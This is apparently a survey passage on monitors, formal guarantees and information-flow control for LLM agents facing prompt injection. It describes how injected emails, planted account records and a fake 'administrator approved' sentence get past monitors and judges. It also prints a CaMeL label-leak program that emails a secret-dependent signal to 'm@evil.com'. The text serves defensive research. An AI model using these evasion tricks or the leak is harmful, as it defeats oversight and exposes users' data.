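Many rules depend on what happened earlier. A shop's agent must identify a customer before it looks up an order, for example, and the lookup call alone doesn't show whether it did. Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, present Agent-C, a monitor for such rules. Its language has five basic forms. "Before" requires an earlier call, "After" requires a later one, and "Seq" requires two calls in order. "Forall" restricts every call to a tool, and "Exists" requires at least one call. Rules can also refer to the results of past calls and to facts in the shop's database. Leaving out some details, the rule about identification becomes

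$$\forall t:\; \textit{tool}_t = \textit{get order} \;\rightarrow\; \exists t' < t:\; \textit{tool}_{t'} = \textit{find user} \,\wedge\, \textit{result}_{t'} = \textit{owner}(\textit{order}_t).$$

In words, whenever the agent looks up an order at step $t$, it must have identified that order's owner at some earlier step $t'$. In one test, a customer named Sofia asks to return a camera and gives an order number, and the agent immediately tries to look up the order. Agent-C handles this as follows:

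1. It extracts the tool's name and arguments while the model is writing the call.
2. It looks up the stored facts that the rules need, in this case who owns the order.
3. It adds the proposed call to the record of past calls and translates the record and the rules into a logical formula.
4. A solver searches for some continuation of the run that satisfies the rules. If it finds one, the call goes ahead.
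5. If it doesn't, Agent-C discards the call and the model tries again.

No continuation can repair Sofia's case, because the record contains no identification and later calls can't change the past. With an open model, Agent-C rewinds the text to just before the tool's name and makes the rejected choice less likely. Providers of closed models don't reveal all the probabilities this requires, so with those models Agent-C requests a new call from the start. On retail tasks with the small open model Qwen3-8B, rewinding raised the share of solved tasks from 36.5% to 42.1% and used 40% fewer output tokens. If every attempt fails, Agent-C records an error message, which the model can read before its next step.

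The soundness theorem states that if a run complies with the rules so far and Agent-C passes a call, the run still complies afterwards. The proof is short because Agent-C passes a call only after a successful solver check. A run complies if some continuation would satisfy the rules. As in MENTOR, this condition is weaker than staying in the winning region of a game, because the solver can assume that other people will answer favourably. A second theorem states that every run that ends normally satisfies all the rules. If the agent tries to stop while a duty is outstanding, Agent-C ends the run in an error state, which the theorem doesn't cover.

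Both theorems are about the formal rules, which can differ from what the shop intended. One retail policy requires refunds to go to the original payment method or an existing gift card. The published formula accepts any payment identifier that contains the text "gift_card". Unless another check confirms that the card belongs to the customer, an attacker could supply someone else's card without violating the formula.

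### Tests on retail and airline tasks

Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C in 2025 on τ-bench, a benchmark in which a language model plays a customer of a shop or an airline. They also wrote 17 adversarial tasks each for the shop and the airline, in which the customer wants something the policy forbids. Except for one column, the table gives results without Agent-C. A task counts as solved only if the agent also followed the rules. With Agent-C, the agents followed the rules in every run and no attack succeeded.

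| Model and setting | Ordinary tasks: rules kept | Ordinary tasks: solved | Solved with Agent-C | Adversarial tasks: rules kept | Adversarial tasks: attack succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, retail | 93.0% | 76.5% | 80.5% | 23.5% | 29.4% |
| GPT-5, retail | 91.9% | 71.0% | 73.6% | 70.6% | 3.9% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5, airline | 70.0% | 42.0% | 43.5% | 47.1% | 11.8% |
| GPT-5, airline | 71.3% | 38.0% | 42.8% | 78.4% | 2.0% |

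Enforcement slightly increased the number of solved tasks. Smaller models gained much more, with Qwen3-8B going from 11.3% to 42.1% on the retail tasks. The additional checks raised the average time for an ordinary task with Qwen3-32B from 333 to 480 seconds.

Without Agent-C, Claude broke a rule in about 76% of the adversarial retail runs, but the attacker reached the goal in only 29%. The zero attack success rates with Agent-C are weaker evidence of protection against attackers than they seem, because Kamath and colleagues count an attack as successful only if the agent both completes the harmful task and breaks the policy. Any monitor that enforces the whole policy must therefore score zero, and the test can't detect an attacker who profits while the agent keeps the rules.

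The researchers also rewrote the policies in AgentSpec's language. With those rules, the three Qwen3 models followed the policy in 84% to 86% of ordinary retail runs and 65% to 79% of ordinary airline runs. A competing team wrote these rules, so better ones might have narrowed the gap.

Newer models still need such checks. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) puts four small programs between an agent and an airline's database. Each program checks one policy rule before the agent can change a booking. The airline's tools carry out any well-formed request, even one the policy forbids. With the small model GPT-4o mini, 78% of failures left the database in a wrong state without any error message. The checks raised that model's share of solved tasks from 29.6% to 42.0%, and the gain was almost the same when the experiment was repeated with new random seeds. For GPT-5.2,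 the share rose from 61.2% to 71.6%, but that experiment was small and the margin of error around the gain almost included zero.

Nearly all of the improvement came from one check, which tests whether a booking is eligible for cancellation and was right all 161 times it blocked a call. Another check was right only 5% of the time. A formal guarantee wouldn't reveal this problem, because blocking too many calls never breaks a prohibition. If one of the checking programs crashes, the call goes ahead, which avoids needless blocks but leaves a gap in the guarantee. Agent-C, by contrast, allows a call only after the solver has found a compliant continuation.

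### Contracts and predictions

A rule may be reasonable only if the agent's environment behaves as expected. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) therefore splits each rule into an assumption about the environment and a guarantee by the agent. For instance, the assumption might be that a policy service supplies valid authorisations, and the guarantee might be that the agent issues refunds only within the authorised limit. If something goes wrong, the operator can tell whether the environment or the agent failed.

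Their system, ContrAgent, writes both parts in temporal logic over exact facts about calls, including counts, amounts and permissions. Like TRAC, it rewrites each formula after every event, and it blocks a call that would reduce a guarantee to "false". The rewriting can be late to detect that a formula can no longer be satisfied, so ContrAgent may allow a call after which a violation is unavoidable. ContrAgent also searches the whole set of contracts for combinations that can't all hold at once. This would help with the conflicting instructions that led the banking agent in the earlier experiments to invent excuses.

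Xiao and colleagues tested ContrAgent with Gemini 2.5 Flash on customer-service tasks in seven fields, such as banking and healthcare. Without the procedures, the agent completed 91% of permitted tasks but withheld only 32% of forbidden ones. Putting the procedures in the prompt raised the share of forbidden tasks withheld to 94%, but the agent refused too much and completed only 64% of permitted tasks. With a second language model judging each call, the agent completed 24% of permitted tasks and withheld 98% of forbidden ones. With ContrAgent, the figures were 90% and 98%. On a weaker model, the prompted agent withheld only 45% of forbidden tasks, while ContrAgent still withheld 98%.

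Wang, Poskitt and colleagues (2025), in *ProbGuard*, try to predict violations instead of checking for them. Their system, earlier called Pro2Guard, describes each situation with a few true-or-false facts. It then uses recorded runs to estimate how often each situation leads to each other one, which gives a small Markov chain. During a run, it intervenes in state $s$ when

$$\Pr(\mathbf{G}\,\neg\textit{unsafe} \mid s) < \theta,$$

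where $\theta$ is a threshold that the operator chooses. Suppose a household robot has left the kitchen with the stove on. At each step it returns with probability 0.3, stays away with probability 0.6, or the food burns with probability 0.1. If we count a return as safe, the probability $p$ that the food eventually burns satisfies $p = 0.1 + 0.6p$, so $p = 0.25$. The robot stays safe with probability 0.75, and a monitor with $\theta = 0.8$ would send it back.

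In simulated household tasks, ProbGuard reduced unsafe behaviour by 65% and kept task completion at 80% of its original level. In simulated driving, it gave up to 15.8 seconds' warning at a threshold that produced no false alarms. Statistical theory shows how many recorded runs are needed for the estimated probabilities to probably be close to the true ones. That result assumes future runs follow the same pattern as the recorded ones, and an attacker can change the pattern. If someone kept calling the robot away so that it never returned, the food would certainly burn, but the monitor would still calculate a 25% chance. Wang and colleagues didn't test ProbGuard against prompt injection.

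The five systems differ in what their rules can express and in what their theory establishes:

| System | Content of a rule | Established result |
|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec | a trigger, conditions on the current situation and a response | in Ray's theory, it can enforce the safety properties that its checks can represent |
| Progent | the tools and argument values that the agent may currently use | permissions never grow without approval |
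| Agent-C | the order of calls, with data from past calls and databases | every run that ends normally satisfies the rules |
| ContrAgent | order, counts and limits, under assumptions about the environment | for safety properties whose assumptions hold, live checks and later replays agree on violations |
| ProbGuard | a set of unsafe states | with enough sample runs, the estimated model is close to the agent's usual behaviour |

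None of these results says that an attacker gains nothing.

### Which rules a gate can enforce

Agent-C and ContrAgent both have trouble with duties that the agent has not yet fulfilled, and Ray's *What Can Be Enforced?* shows why. It considers a gate, which is a monitor that must decide on each call before the call has an irreversible effect. The gate must ensure that the calls that take effect never break the rule, whatever the agent proposes. It must also let all of the agent's proposals through unchanged if they comply with the rule. Without this second requirement, a gate that blocks every call would enforce any prohibition.

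The beginning of a run is acceptable if at least one continuation of it satisfies the rule. Ray proves that, given accurate facts, a gate can meet both demands if and only if the rule is a safety property and a program can recognise the acceptable beginnings. One half of the proof describes the gate, which runs this program and blocks any call that would make the beginning unacceptable.

A gate can't enforce the rule that every payment is eventually confirmed without interfering with agents that comply. Suppose one agent proposes a payment and then a confirmation. Its run complies, so the gate must allow the payment. Another agent proposes the same payment and then does nothing. The two runs are identical up to the payment, so the gate must allow this one too, and the second agent breaks the rule. Blocking the payment would also have stopped the first agent's compliant run.

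The same argument applies to every rule that isn't a safety property. Each such rule has a violating run that could, at every step, still be continued into a compliant one. The gate has to allow each step because a compliant run could begin the same way, so it allows the whole violating run. Randomizing the gate's decisions doesn't help, because it must still allow compliant runs with certainty.

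A monitor can enforce the rule if it can hold the payment until the confirmation arrives, but this only works for actions that can wait. Otherwise, the operator has to change the rule. A gate could require the confirmation before the payment, or block a second payment until the agent has confirmed the first. The second option still allows at most one unconfirmed payment.

The recognition condition also limits what the gate can enforce. To enforce a daily limit per recipient, the gate needs a running total for each recipient and day, and a clock that the agent can't change. Some rule languages are so expressive that no program can always determine whether a set of rules forbids anything.

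Ray's theory also assumes that blocking a call is harmless. This assumption fails in cases like the earlier email assistant, where a message already in the outbox is sent even if the assistant does nothing, and such cases need reactive synthesis.

### Where the facts come from

*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) tested whether existing records of attacks contain the facts that such rules need. Recorded runs were replayed through MonPoly, an established monitor for temporal logic with data and time limits. The runs came from AgentDojo and from STAC, a collection of attacks in which ordinary-looking calls combine to cause harm. Each of the five general rules required prior approval for one kind of risky action, such as deleting something, paying money or sending data out.

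The monitor raised an alarm in 70.1% of the 1,931 successful AgentDojo attacks on GPT-4o and in 71.8% of the 483 STAC attacks. It also raised an alarm in 29.3% of the harmless AgentDojo runs. If one run in a hundred contained a successful attack, only about 2.4% of the alarms would come from runs with successful attacks. In the banking tasks, the monitor caught 97.4% of the successful attacks but would have interrupted 79.2% of the harmless runs.

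MonPoly applied the rules correctly. A version with a machine-checked algorithm and an unrelated monitor both raised alarms on the same STAC attacks. But the records contain hardly any approvals. None of the 6,899 AgentDojo runs in the study has one, because the user sends a single message at the start and cannot approve anything later. The condition "without earlier approval" is therefore always true, and the rule reduces to a ban on risky actions. The records also lack timestamps, so nobody can use them to test a rule such as "the consent must be less than 24 hours old". In τ-bench, where the customer talks with the agent throughout, 52.5% of the recorded runs contain an approval before the agent changes any data.

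Some AgentDojo records do show where a payment's recipient came from. Kekatos and colleagues used this for a more precise rule,

$$\mathbf{G}\,\forall p\,\big(\textit{transfer}(p) \rightarrow \mathbf{O}\,\textit{known}(p)\big),$$

where $\mathbf{O}$ means "at this step or some earlier one". The agent may pay $p$ only if $p$ has already appeared as a sender or recipient in account data. Compared with the general rule about payments, this reduced alarms on harmless banking runs from 44% to 24%. The share of successful attacks it caught fell from 79% to 70%.

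But an attacker can write to the record that the monitor relies on. Adding one line that listed the attacker's account in the format of real account data made the monitor accept 94% of the transfers it had previously flagged. In the corresponding test on email recipients, it accepted 99%. The formula still held in these runs, because the planted line had made $\textit{known}(p)$ true.

The researchers repaired the rule by counting a recipient as known only if a lookup made by the agent itself had returned the name. None of the planted lines worked after that, and the numbers of caught attacks and false alarms stayed the same. The two versions give identical results on records without the planted lines, so an ordinary benchmark would not have shown that the original was insecure. The repaired rule still fails if the attacker controls the tool that answers the lookup. Kekatos and colleagues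 propose that benchmarks record twelve facts about every event, including its time, source, any approval and how far the monitor can trust it.

### When a fallible judge supplies a fact

A gate for the rule about personal data needs a fallible judge, usually a language model, to give each proposed call a risk score. The gate blocks calls whose score reaches a threshold. Lowering the threshold reduces misses (violations that get through) but increases false blocks (harmless calls that the gate stops). Ray uses the Neyman–Pearson lemma to show that, for any permitted miss rate $\beta$, there is a lowest rate of false blocks that any gate using the same information can achieve.

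Catching more violations means blocking more harmless calls. One of Ray's simulated judges gives scores that follow a bell curve around 0 for harmless calls and around 2.5 for violations, both with standard deviation 1. A miss rate of 5% requires a threshold of about 0.86, at which the gate blocks 20% of harmless calls. A miss rate of 1% requires a threshold of 0.17, and the gate then blocks 43%. If an attacker can make the agent propose a violation at each of 20 steps, and the judge's errors are independent, keeping the chance that any violation gets through to at most 5% requires a miss rate of only 0.26% per step. The gate then blocks 62% of harmless calls.

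In practice nobody knows the curves, so the operator calibrates the threshold on $n$ sample violations. To keep the miss rate at or below $\delta$, the operator sets the threshold at the $k$-th lowest sample score, where $k = \lfloor (n+1)\delta \rfloor$. If a new violation comes from the same source as the samples, its score is equally likely to take any of the $n+1$ possible ranks. The chance that it falls below the threshold is therefore at most $k/(n+1) \le \delta$, whatever the shape of the curves.

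With few samples, however, $k$ can be zero, and the only threshold that meets the target is one that blocks everything. A target of 5% requires at least 19 sample violations, and dividing that target evenly over 20 steps raises the minimum to 399. The operator can avoid this increase by calibrating on whole runs, but then whole sample runs have to resemble whole future runs.

Ray calibrated 23 language models as judges on 97 user requests and 35 attackers' goals from AgentDojo, using half of the 35 goals as samples each time. With so few samples, all 23 gates blocked everything at a target of 5%, as the formula predicts. At 10%, a gate based on Gemma-2-9B missed about 1% of the violations but blocked 78% of the harmless requests. The judges saw only short instructions, so a deployed judge that also sees the context of a real run might do better.

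The certificate no longer applies if an attacker can change what the judge reads. Suppose the attacker can raise the miss rate by at most $\eta$ at any threshold. Over $H$ steps, the bound on the chance of a violation weakens from $\delta$ to

$$\delta + H\eta.$$

The operator can compensate with a stricter threshold only if $\eta$ is known and smaller than $\delta/H$. Ray added a 16-token sentence claiming that an administrator had already approved the action, which raised the miss rate of 8 of 11 judges by 20 to 60 percentage points at a fixed threshold. A larger search could find sentences that raise the miss rate further, so experiments like this give only a lower bound on $\eta$. If disguised violations get the same range of scores as harmless calls, the monitor must block every call to catch all the violations.

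Blocking a call also changes what the agent does next. One agent may give up while another tries a different route to the same goal, even if the two behave identically when nothing is blocked. We therefore can't fully predict from recorded runs how well a gate will work. Ray ran a small agent through 949 AgentDojo scenarios with and without a gate. A gate with a three-billion-parameter judge reduced successful attacks from 45 to 4, but it blocked 78% of calls and lowered task success from 25% to 18%. A gate with a larger judge blocked only 12% of calls, but 30 attacks still succeeded, which may not be a real improvement. In a paired comparison of 389 scenarios, the larger judge's gate prevented 29 attacks, but 22 others succeeded only when it was in place.

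### Attacks that break no rule

Attacks can succeed even when a monitor enforces its rules perfectly. Xiao and colleagues replayed recorded AgentDojo attacks on 22 models through ContrAgent. Their contracts blocked a call with side effects if its target, such as an email address, had appeared in a tool's output but not in the user's message, and was not among the task's legitimate targets. This reduced the attack success rate from 18.0% to 5.3%, with false alarms in 0.8% of harmless runs. The researchers took the legitimate targets partly from the benchmark's solutions, which a deployed monitor wouldn't have. Contracts derived from the attacks reduced the rate to 1.7%, but the researchers tested them on those same attacks.

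Of the attacks that still succeeded, 82% involved no malicious tool call. Some diverted the agent from its task, and others achieved their aim in the agent's written reply. In the other 18%, the injection got the agent to make a call whose arguments were all legitimate. For example, an injected email might get an assistant to send a confidential file to a colleague the user writes to. The recipient is on every approved list, and the call looks the same as one the user requested.

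Knowing who gave the instruction can help a judge tell an authorised call from an identical unauthorised one. Ray tested this with pairs of identical calls, one instructed by the user and the other by a tool's output. A judge given only the call can do no better than chance. When also given the source, a seven-billion-parameter model gave the unauthorised call the higher risk score in 116 of 123 pairs, while a half-billion-parameter model gave both calls the same score in every pair. The larger model did well but is fallible, and an attacker could also try to disguise where an instruction came from. A guarantee would need software that tracks the source itself.

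## Can the software around a model be secure whatever the model outputs?

Software can record where each piece of data came from without consulting the model. If it also controls which actions that data may influence, we can prove some properties of the whole system while assuming the worst about the model. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025), a commentary on a research paper of the same title, recommends assuming that anyone who gets text in front of a model has full control of its output, including its tool calls. Security then depends on how much damage the rest of the program lets a hijacked model do.

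### Noninterference and labels

Noninterference is the property that untrusted data cannot affect a protected part of a system's behaviour. Let $t$ be the trusted input, such as the user's request, and $u$ the untrusted input, such as the day's email. Let $P(t,u)$ be the protected behaviour, for example the list of tool calls and their recipients. Noninterference requires

$$P(t,u) = P(t,u') \quad\text{for all } t, u, u'.$$

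An attacker who can write any $u$ then has no influence over $P$. If the model chooses its words at random, the two sides of the equation are probability distributions. The same equation means that the attacker learns nothing about secret data if $u$ is that data and $P$ is everything the attacker can observe. Since the definition compares two runs, no monitor can detect a violation from a single trace.

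Information-flow control enforces such properties with labels. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the usual pair, an integrity label (trusted or untrusted) and a confidentiality label (public or secret). When a program combines two values, the result is untrusted if either value is untrusted, and secret if either is secret. A confidentiality label can also list the permitted readers. If Ana, Ben and Carla may read one document, and Ben, Carla and Dan may read another, only Ben and Carla may read a text based on both.

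It is hard to tell which parts of the input a language model used, so the software normally gives the output the combined label of everything the model read. Once an ordinary agent reads one email from a stranger, its next tool call is untrusted. A rule that only trusted calls may have consequences would then stop the agent, even if the email was harmless.

### An email task from request to message

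The usual remedy is the dual-LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model plans and calls tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use the example of a user who wants a summary of recent emails about a project sent to a manager. One of the emails contains an instruction to forward the top message in the mailbox to an outsider. A system that separates the plan from the emails would proceed as follows:

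1. The privileged model reads only the user's request. It plans to fetch the emails, have them summarised and send the summary to the manager.
2. The software fetches the emails, labels them untrusted and stores them in a variable. The privileged model sees only the variable's name.
3. The quarantined model reads the emails and writes a summary. It may try to obey the injected instruction, but it has no tool for forwarding anything. The software stores its output in a second untrusted variable.
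4. The privileged model requests a message to the manager with the second variable as the text. The software checks that the tool and the recipient are trusted and that the manager may read the emails behind the summary.
5. The software inserts the summary and sends the message.

The injected email can't affect which tools the agent uses or who receives the message. It can still make the summary false or empty, because the policy allows untrusted text in the message.

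Some plans depend on what the emails contain. Suppose the user wants a calendar entry if any of three emails proposes a meeting. The privileged model can send the quarantined model a yes-or-no question, and the software ensures that only "yes" or "no" comes back. The attacker may control the answer but can't fit an instruction into it. An answer chosen from $n$ options carries at most $\log_2 n$ bits. The quarantined model then extracts the date and the participants into a variable that the planner never sees. The attacker may control these values too, unless the policy requires them to be trusted.

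### FIDES

FIDES, a system Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, checks labels before every tool call. It hides a tool's result in a variable only when showing it to the model would make the conversation less trusted.

Its formal guarantee is explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. Suppose an agent reads a confidential test result and then books either a specialist or a routine appointment. Explicit secrecy rules out copying the result into the booking, which would be an explicit flow of information. The choice of appointment also reveals something about the result, but explicit secrecy permits this because the flow is implicit. For any fixed sequence of tool calls, it requires the publicly visible effects to be the same whatever the secret data contain. Costa and colleagues settled for this property because noninterference would forbid nearly every publicly visible action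 after the agent had read a secret.

The tests of FIDES used AgentDojo with GPT-4o and one fixed style of attack. 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its policy checks off, and none with them on. These counts exclude attacks that AgentDojo scored as successes but that broke no policy, including some that only altered text. The table shows the share of tasks completed with no attack.

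| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, with label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Averaged over the four columns, separating the plan from the data raises task completion from 42% to 50%, which is still about 34 percentage points below the 84% completed without the security measures. Part of this gap is due to GPT-4o's trouble with variables. With the reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%.

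### CaMeL and the gaps in its tracking

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Google DeepMind, 2025) presents CaMeL, in which a privileged model writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs this program and tags every value with its sources and permitted readers, as described in *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026). Before each tool call, a policy function inspects the tags and allows or denies the call.

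The tags stop an attack that separation alone would miss. Suppose the plan is to find Bob's address in a chat channel and write to him. An attacker can post a false address there and receive the message without changing the plan. The policy can deny the call because the address is tagged as coming from an untrusted source.

*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo tasks with no successful injection within its threat model, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. CaMeL used almost three times as many tokens as the undefended agent. Task completion dropped more when Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with two newer models. Both models completed 37.5% of tasks with the policies on, and 67% and 71% with them off.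 There are only 16 banking tasks, so the margins of error are wide, and several require the agent to act on an untrusted file.

CaMeL has no soundness theorem, and Garby and colleagues found leaks in its tracking. One is a variant of a trick known since the 1970s. In outline, the program is:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
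```

If the balance is high, the third line makes `tmp` false and secret, so the program skips the assignment in the fourth line. CaMeL updates labels only for assignments that run, so `rich` stays true and public, and the program sends the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and the program sends nothing. The attacker learns whether the balance is high, although no secret value reached the email tool.

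The loop that retries failed plans runs outside the interpreter and creates a second leak. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal that secret one bit at a time. To use either leak, an attacker would first have to get suitable code into the plan, which CaMeL's separation makes difficult.

### A noninterference theorem for agents that write code

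Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, in which such leaks can't occur unnoticed. The language has instructions for prompting a model, copying a conversation and clearing it, and every value carries a label. If a program tries to change a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret, the interpreter stops it.

Their main theorem covers every program in the language, including code that the model writes during the run. Take two runs whose inputs look the same to an observer, and let $\mu$ and $\nu$ give the probability of each result as that observer sees it. The probabilities may add up to less than one, because some runs never finish or violate a policy and stop. The theorem states that a single distribution $\omega$, with a total of at most one, satisfies

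$$\mu \le \omega \quad\text{and}\quad \nu \le \omega$$

for every result. If both programs always finish, this forces $\mu = \nu$, which is noninterference. Otherwise the statistical distance between $\mu$ and $\nu$ is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. If each program fails to finish 10% of the time, the probability of any observable outcome can differ by at most 10 percentage points.

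The proof is machine-checked in Lean and applies to the interpreter that actually calls the model. The guarantee still depends on the developer labeling the data sources correctly and putting checks on the sensitive tools.

Many useful tasks require an agent to act on untrusted data, so LLMbda has an instruction, `endorse`, that declares an untrusted value trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsing a value can never expose a secret, but the theorem does not protect the agent's actions. In tests with three models on the banking tasks, the attacker succeeded in 2 of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user asked the agent to make a payment following instructions in a text file, but the attacker had replaced the file and the agent endorsed its contents. Removing `endorse` blocks this attack, but it lowered the share of tasks Qwen3.7-plus completed from 75% to 62.5%.

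With endorsement allowed, GPT-5.2 completed 75% of the banking tasks, about as many as CaMeL completed without its policies. Garby and colleagues also found that in 97 of the 144 task-attack pairs, the attack needed a tool call or file read that the plan would not normally contain. Separation usually defeats those attacks before any label matters, so a low overall attack success rate is weak evidence of good labels.

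### Comparing an agent with one that ignores injections

Noninterference also forbids some disclosures that the user wants. For example, a calendar assistant may be meant to send the user's free times to anyone who requests a meeting, even though they are private data. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) therefore compares the agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and monitor but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is relatively secure if an injection never lets an attacker distinguish two possible values of the user's data that the attacker couldn't distinguish using the reference agent. An injection that extracts the user's free times passes this test because an ordinary meeting request would also reveal them, but one that extracts a password reset code fails because the reference agent would not reveal the code.

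Dongol's main theorem is about a fence, a monitor that withdraws tools. Every plan is relatively secure if, by the first untrusted read, the monitor has permanently revoked every tool an injection could call. If it revokes them later, the agent could read an untrusted email and then a secret, and an injected call could send the secret before the monitor revokes the tools.

User approval is more flexible, but its wording matters too. Approval of "the next message" lets an injected call send private data, whereas approval of an exact message lets it send only that message. An attacker who can time the message may still learn whether a secret equals its text.

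The fence theorem is machine-checked, but it assumes that each injection triggers a single call and that when the model follows an injection doesn't depend on secrets. It covers leaks but not other harms, such as an injection that deletes files. It also doesn't require the agent to be useful. Because the reference agent works under the same monitor, a monitor that blocks every call counts as perfectly secure.

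### Checking a plan before it runs

Because CaMeL's plans are programs, software can inspect them before any tool runs. CaMeLoT, the extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, turns each plan into a finite-state machine with a state for every point in the program. It treats each branch as able to go either way and each loop as able to run any number of times, so the machine includes every order of calls the plan could produce. This is the step condition, which is manageable for a short program. A standard model checker then explores the machine. One rule for an agent that handles security alerts is

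$$\mathbf{AG}\big(\textit{create ticket} \rightarrow \mathbf{AF}(\textit{resolve} \vee \textit{escalate})\big),$$

where $\mathbf{A}$ means "on every path". A gate can't enforce such a rule without obstructing agents that comply, but CaMeLoT can check it because the whole plan is available in advance. The result assumes that each call does what its name suggests, because CaMeLoT doesn't model what happens inside a tool. If a plan fails, the privileged model receives the offending path and rewrites the plan.

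CaMeLoT could express 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies. Most of the rest depend on facts known only during the run, such as who can read a file. Of 97 tasks without attacks, both systems let the agent complete 42 and blocked 17. They disagreed on 16, and in the other 22 the plan didn't do what the user wanted. In a security-operations scenario, CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one, but the researchers had chosen rules that CaMeL wasn't designed to express.

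### Proving the enclosing program correct

A bug in the surrounding software could make any of these designs insecure. Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, address this by verifying PocketFlow, a very small framework for building agents. Their proof represents the model as an empty procedure that may return any action of the permitted types. The policy allows the agent to read files only inside one folder, call only listed tools and take only a limited number of steps.

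The theorem states that the policy $\Pi(s,a,e,s')$ holds at every step for every sequence of actions, where $s$ is the program's state, $a$ is the model's action, $e$ is the resulting external effect and $s'$ is the next state. The proof matches each step of the program's detailed model with a step of a simpler specification that obeys the policy. The proof places no restriction on $a$, so the guarantee would still hold for a more capable model.

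The main assumption is that every external effect passes through the verified interface. The theorem doesn't cover the Python runtime or the operating system. The interface also needs to be narrow, because the theorem guarantees almost nothing if one of the permitted actions is "run any command".

Language models wrote the specification and the proof, and the Dafny verifier checked them. That check doesn't show that the specification is meaningful. In one variant of the experiment, the models never filled in a field that a safety rule referred to, so the rule held for every run and protected nothing. The specification still passed all three of the researchers' quality tests.

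### Trust levels inside the attention computation

Gupta (2025), in *Can AI Keep a Secret?*, tries to build the separation into the model itself. A transformer represents each token by a list of numbers, its hidden state, and uses a mechanism called attention to update that state with a weighted mix of information from other tokens. Gupta's method, CIV, gives each token a trust level, from web pages at the bottom to the operator's instructions at the top, and sets some of the attention weights to zero. The theorem states that if token $p$ has lower trust than token $q$, then

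$$\frac{\partial H_q^{(N)}}{\partial e_p} = 0,$$

where $e_p$ is the numerical input for $p$ and $H_q^{(N)}$ is the final hidden state of $q$. In other words, a web page can't change how the model represents the operator's instructions.

The theorem doesn't limit what the model writes. Each generated token takes the lowest trust level in the preceding text, so once the context contains a web page, the reply is no more trusted than the page and the theorem doesn't protect it. The models Gupta modified process text from left to right, so a token's hidden state never depends on later tokens. If the operator's instructions come before the web page, an unmodified model already satisfies the equation, but unmodified models still follow injections.

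The proof also doesn't match the published formula. The proof requires that low-trust tokens can't influence high-trust ones, while the formula stops high-trust tokens from influencing low-trust ones. Under either version, the web page can still influence the reply. CIV blocked all 346 attacks from two fixed collections but doubled the response time. The theorem doesn't explain why the attacks failed, and an adaptive attacker might do better.

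### What injected text can still change

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025), the paper Willison comments on, describes six ways to build agents so that untrusted text can't trigger harmful actions. Most of the patterns leave the attacker some influence.

| Pattern | Restriction | Remaining influence |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from fixed actions and never sees their results | A user's own message can still affect which listed action it picks |
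| Plan then execute | The model fixes its tool calls before reading untrusted data | The data can change the contents of a call, such as an email's text |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns, say, yes or no | A document can get itself misclassified, for instance as an invoice |
| Dual LLM | The planner handles untrusted text only by reference | The text can change the values that the planner passes on |
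| Code then execute | The model writes a program before reading untrusted data | The data can change the values inside the program |
| Context minimisation | The software deletes the user's message before the model writes its reply | The message can still shape the database query that it led to |

How much this influence matters depends on the task. A misfiled invoice is a nuisance, but a false summary of a contract could cost the user a lot of money even if the model makes no forbidden tool call.

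Strict limits on the format of untrusted data help, though short strings can still carry instructions. For a programming agent, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest converting untrusted documentation into a list of functions with names of at most 30 characters. Willison points out that an attacker could name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance` and hope that the agent runs `rm -rf`, a command that deletes files.

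The payment file that defeated Garby and colleagues' agent is a similar case. The CaMeL paper reports that the same attack succeeded and places it outside the threat model. If a user tells an agent to follow a document that an attacker wrote, labels can only be used to block the payment or allow it, because telling a false invoice from a real one requires judging its content.

### Adaptive attacks and lost tasks

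Defenders reply that such attacks are much harder to carry out than attacks on a model that obeys any instruction. Rewording an injection doesn't help if the label or permission stays the same, so the attacker has to reach the goal through permitted actions or corrupt the information a check relies on. Narisetty and colleagues find this plausible but largely untested, since most published results for defences outside the model come from tests against fixed attacks.

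They ran an adaptive test of one such defence, Progent, with a small open model as the agent. Progent reduced the average attack success rate on three groups of AgentDojo tasks from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack written to fool the model that revises Progent's permissions succeeded 2.6% of the time. This evidence is encouraging but weak, because the researchers, who build security tools of this kind, used a single handwritten template, and its harmless-sounding wording may have made the agent less likely to obey it. They also didn't test attacks that use only permitted calls. Progent reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 45% to 27% and needed about 15 times as many model calls.

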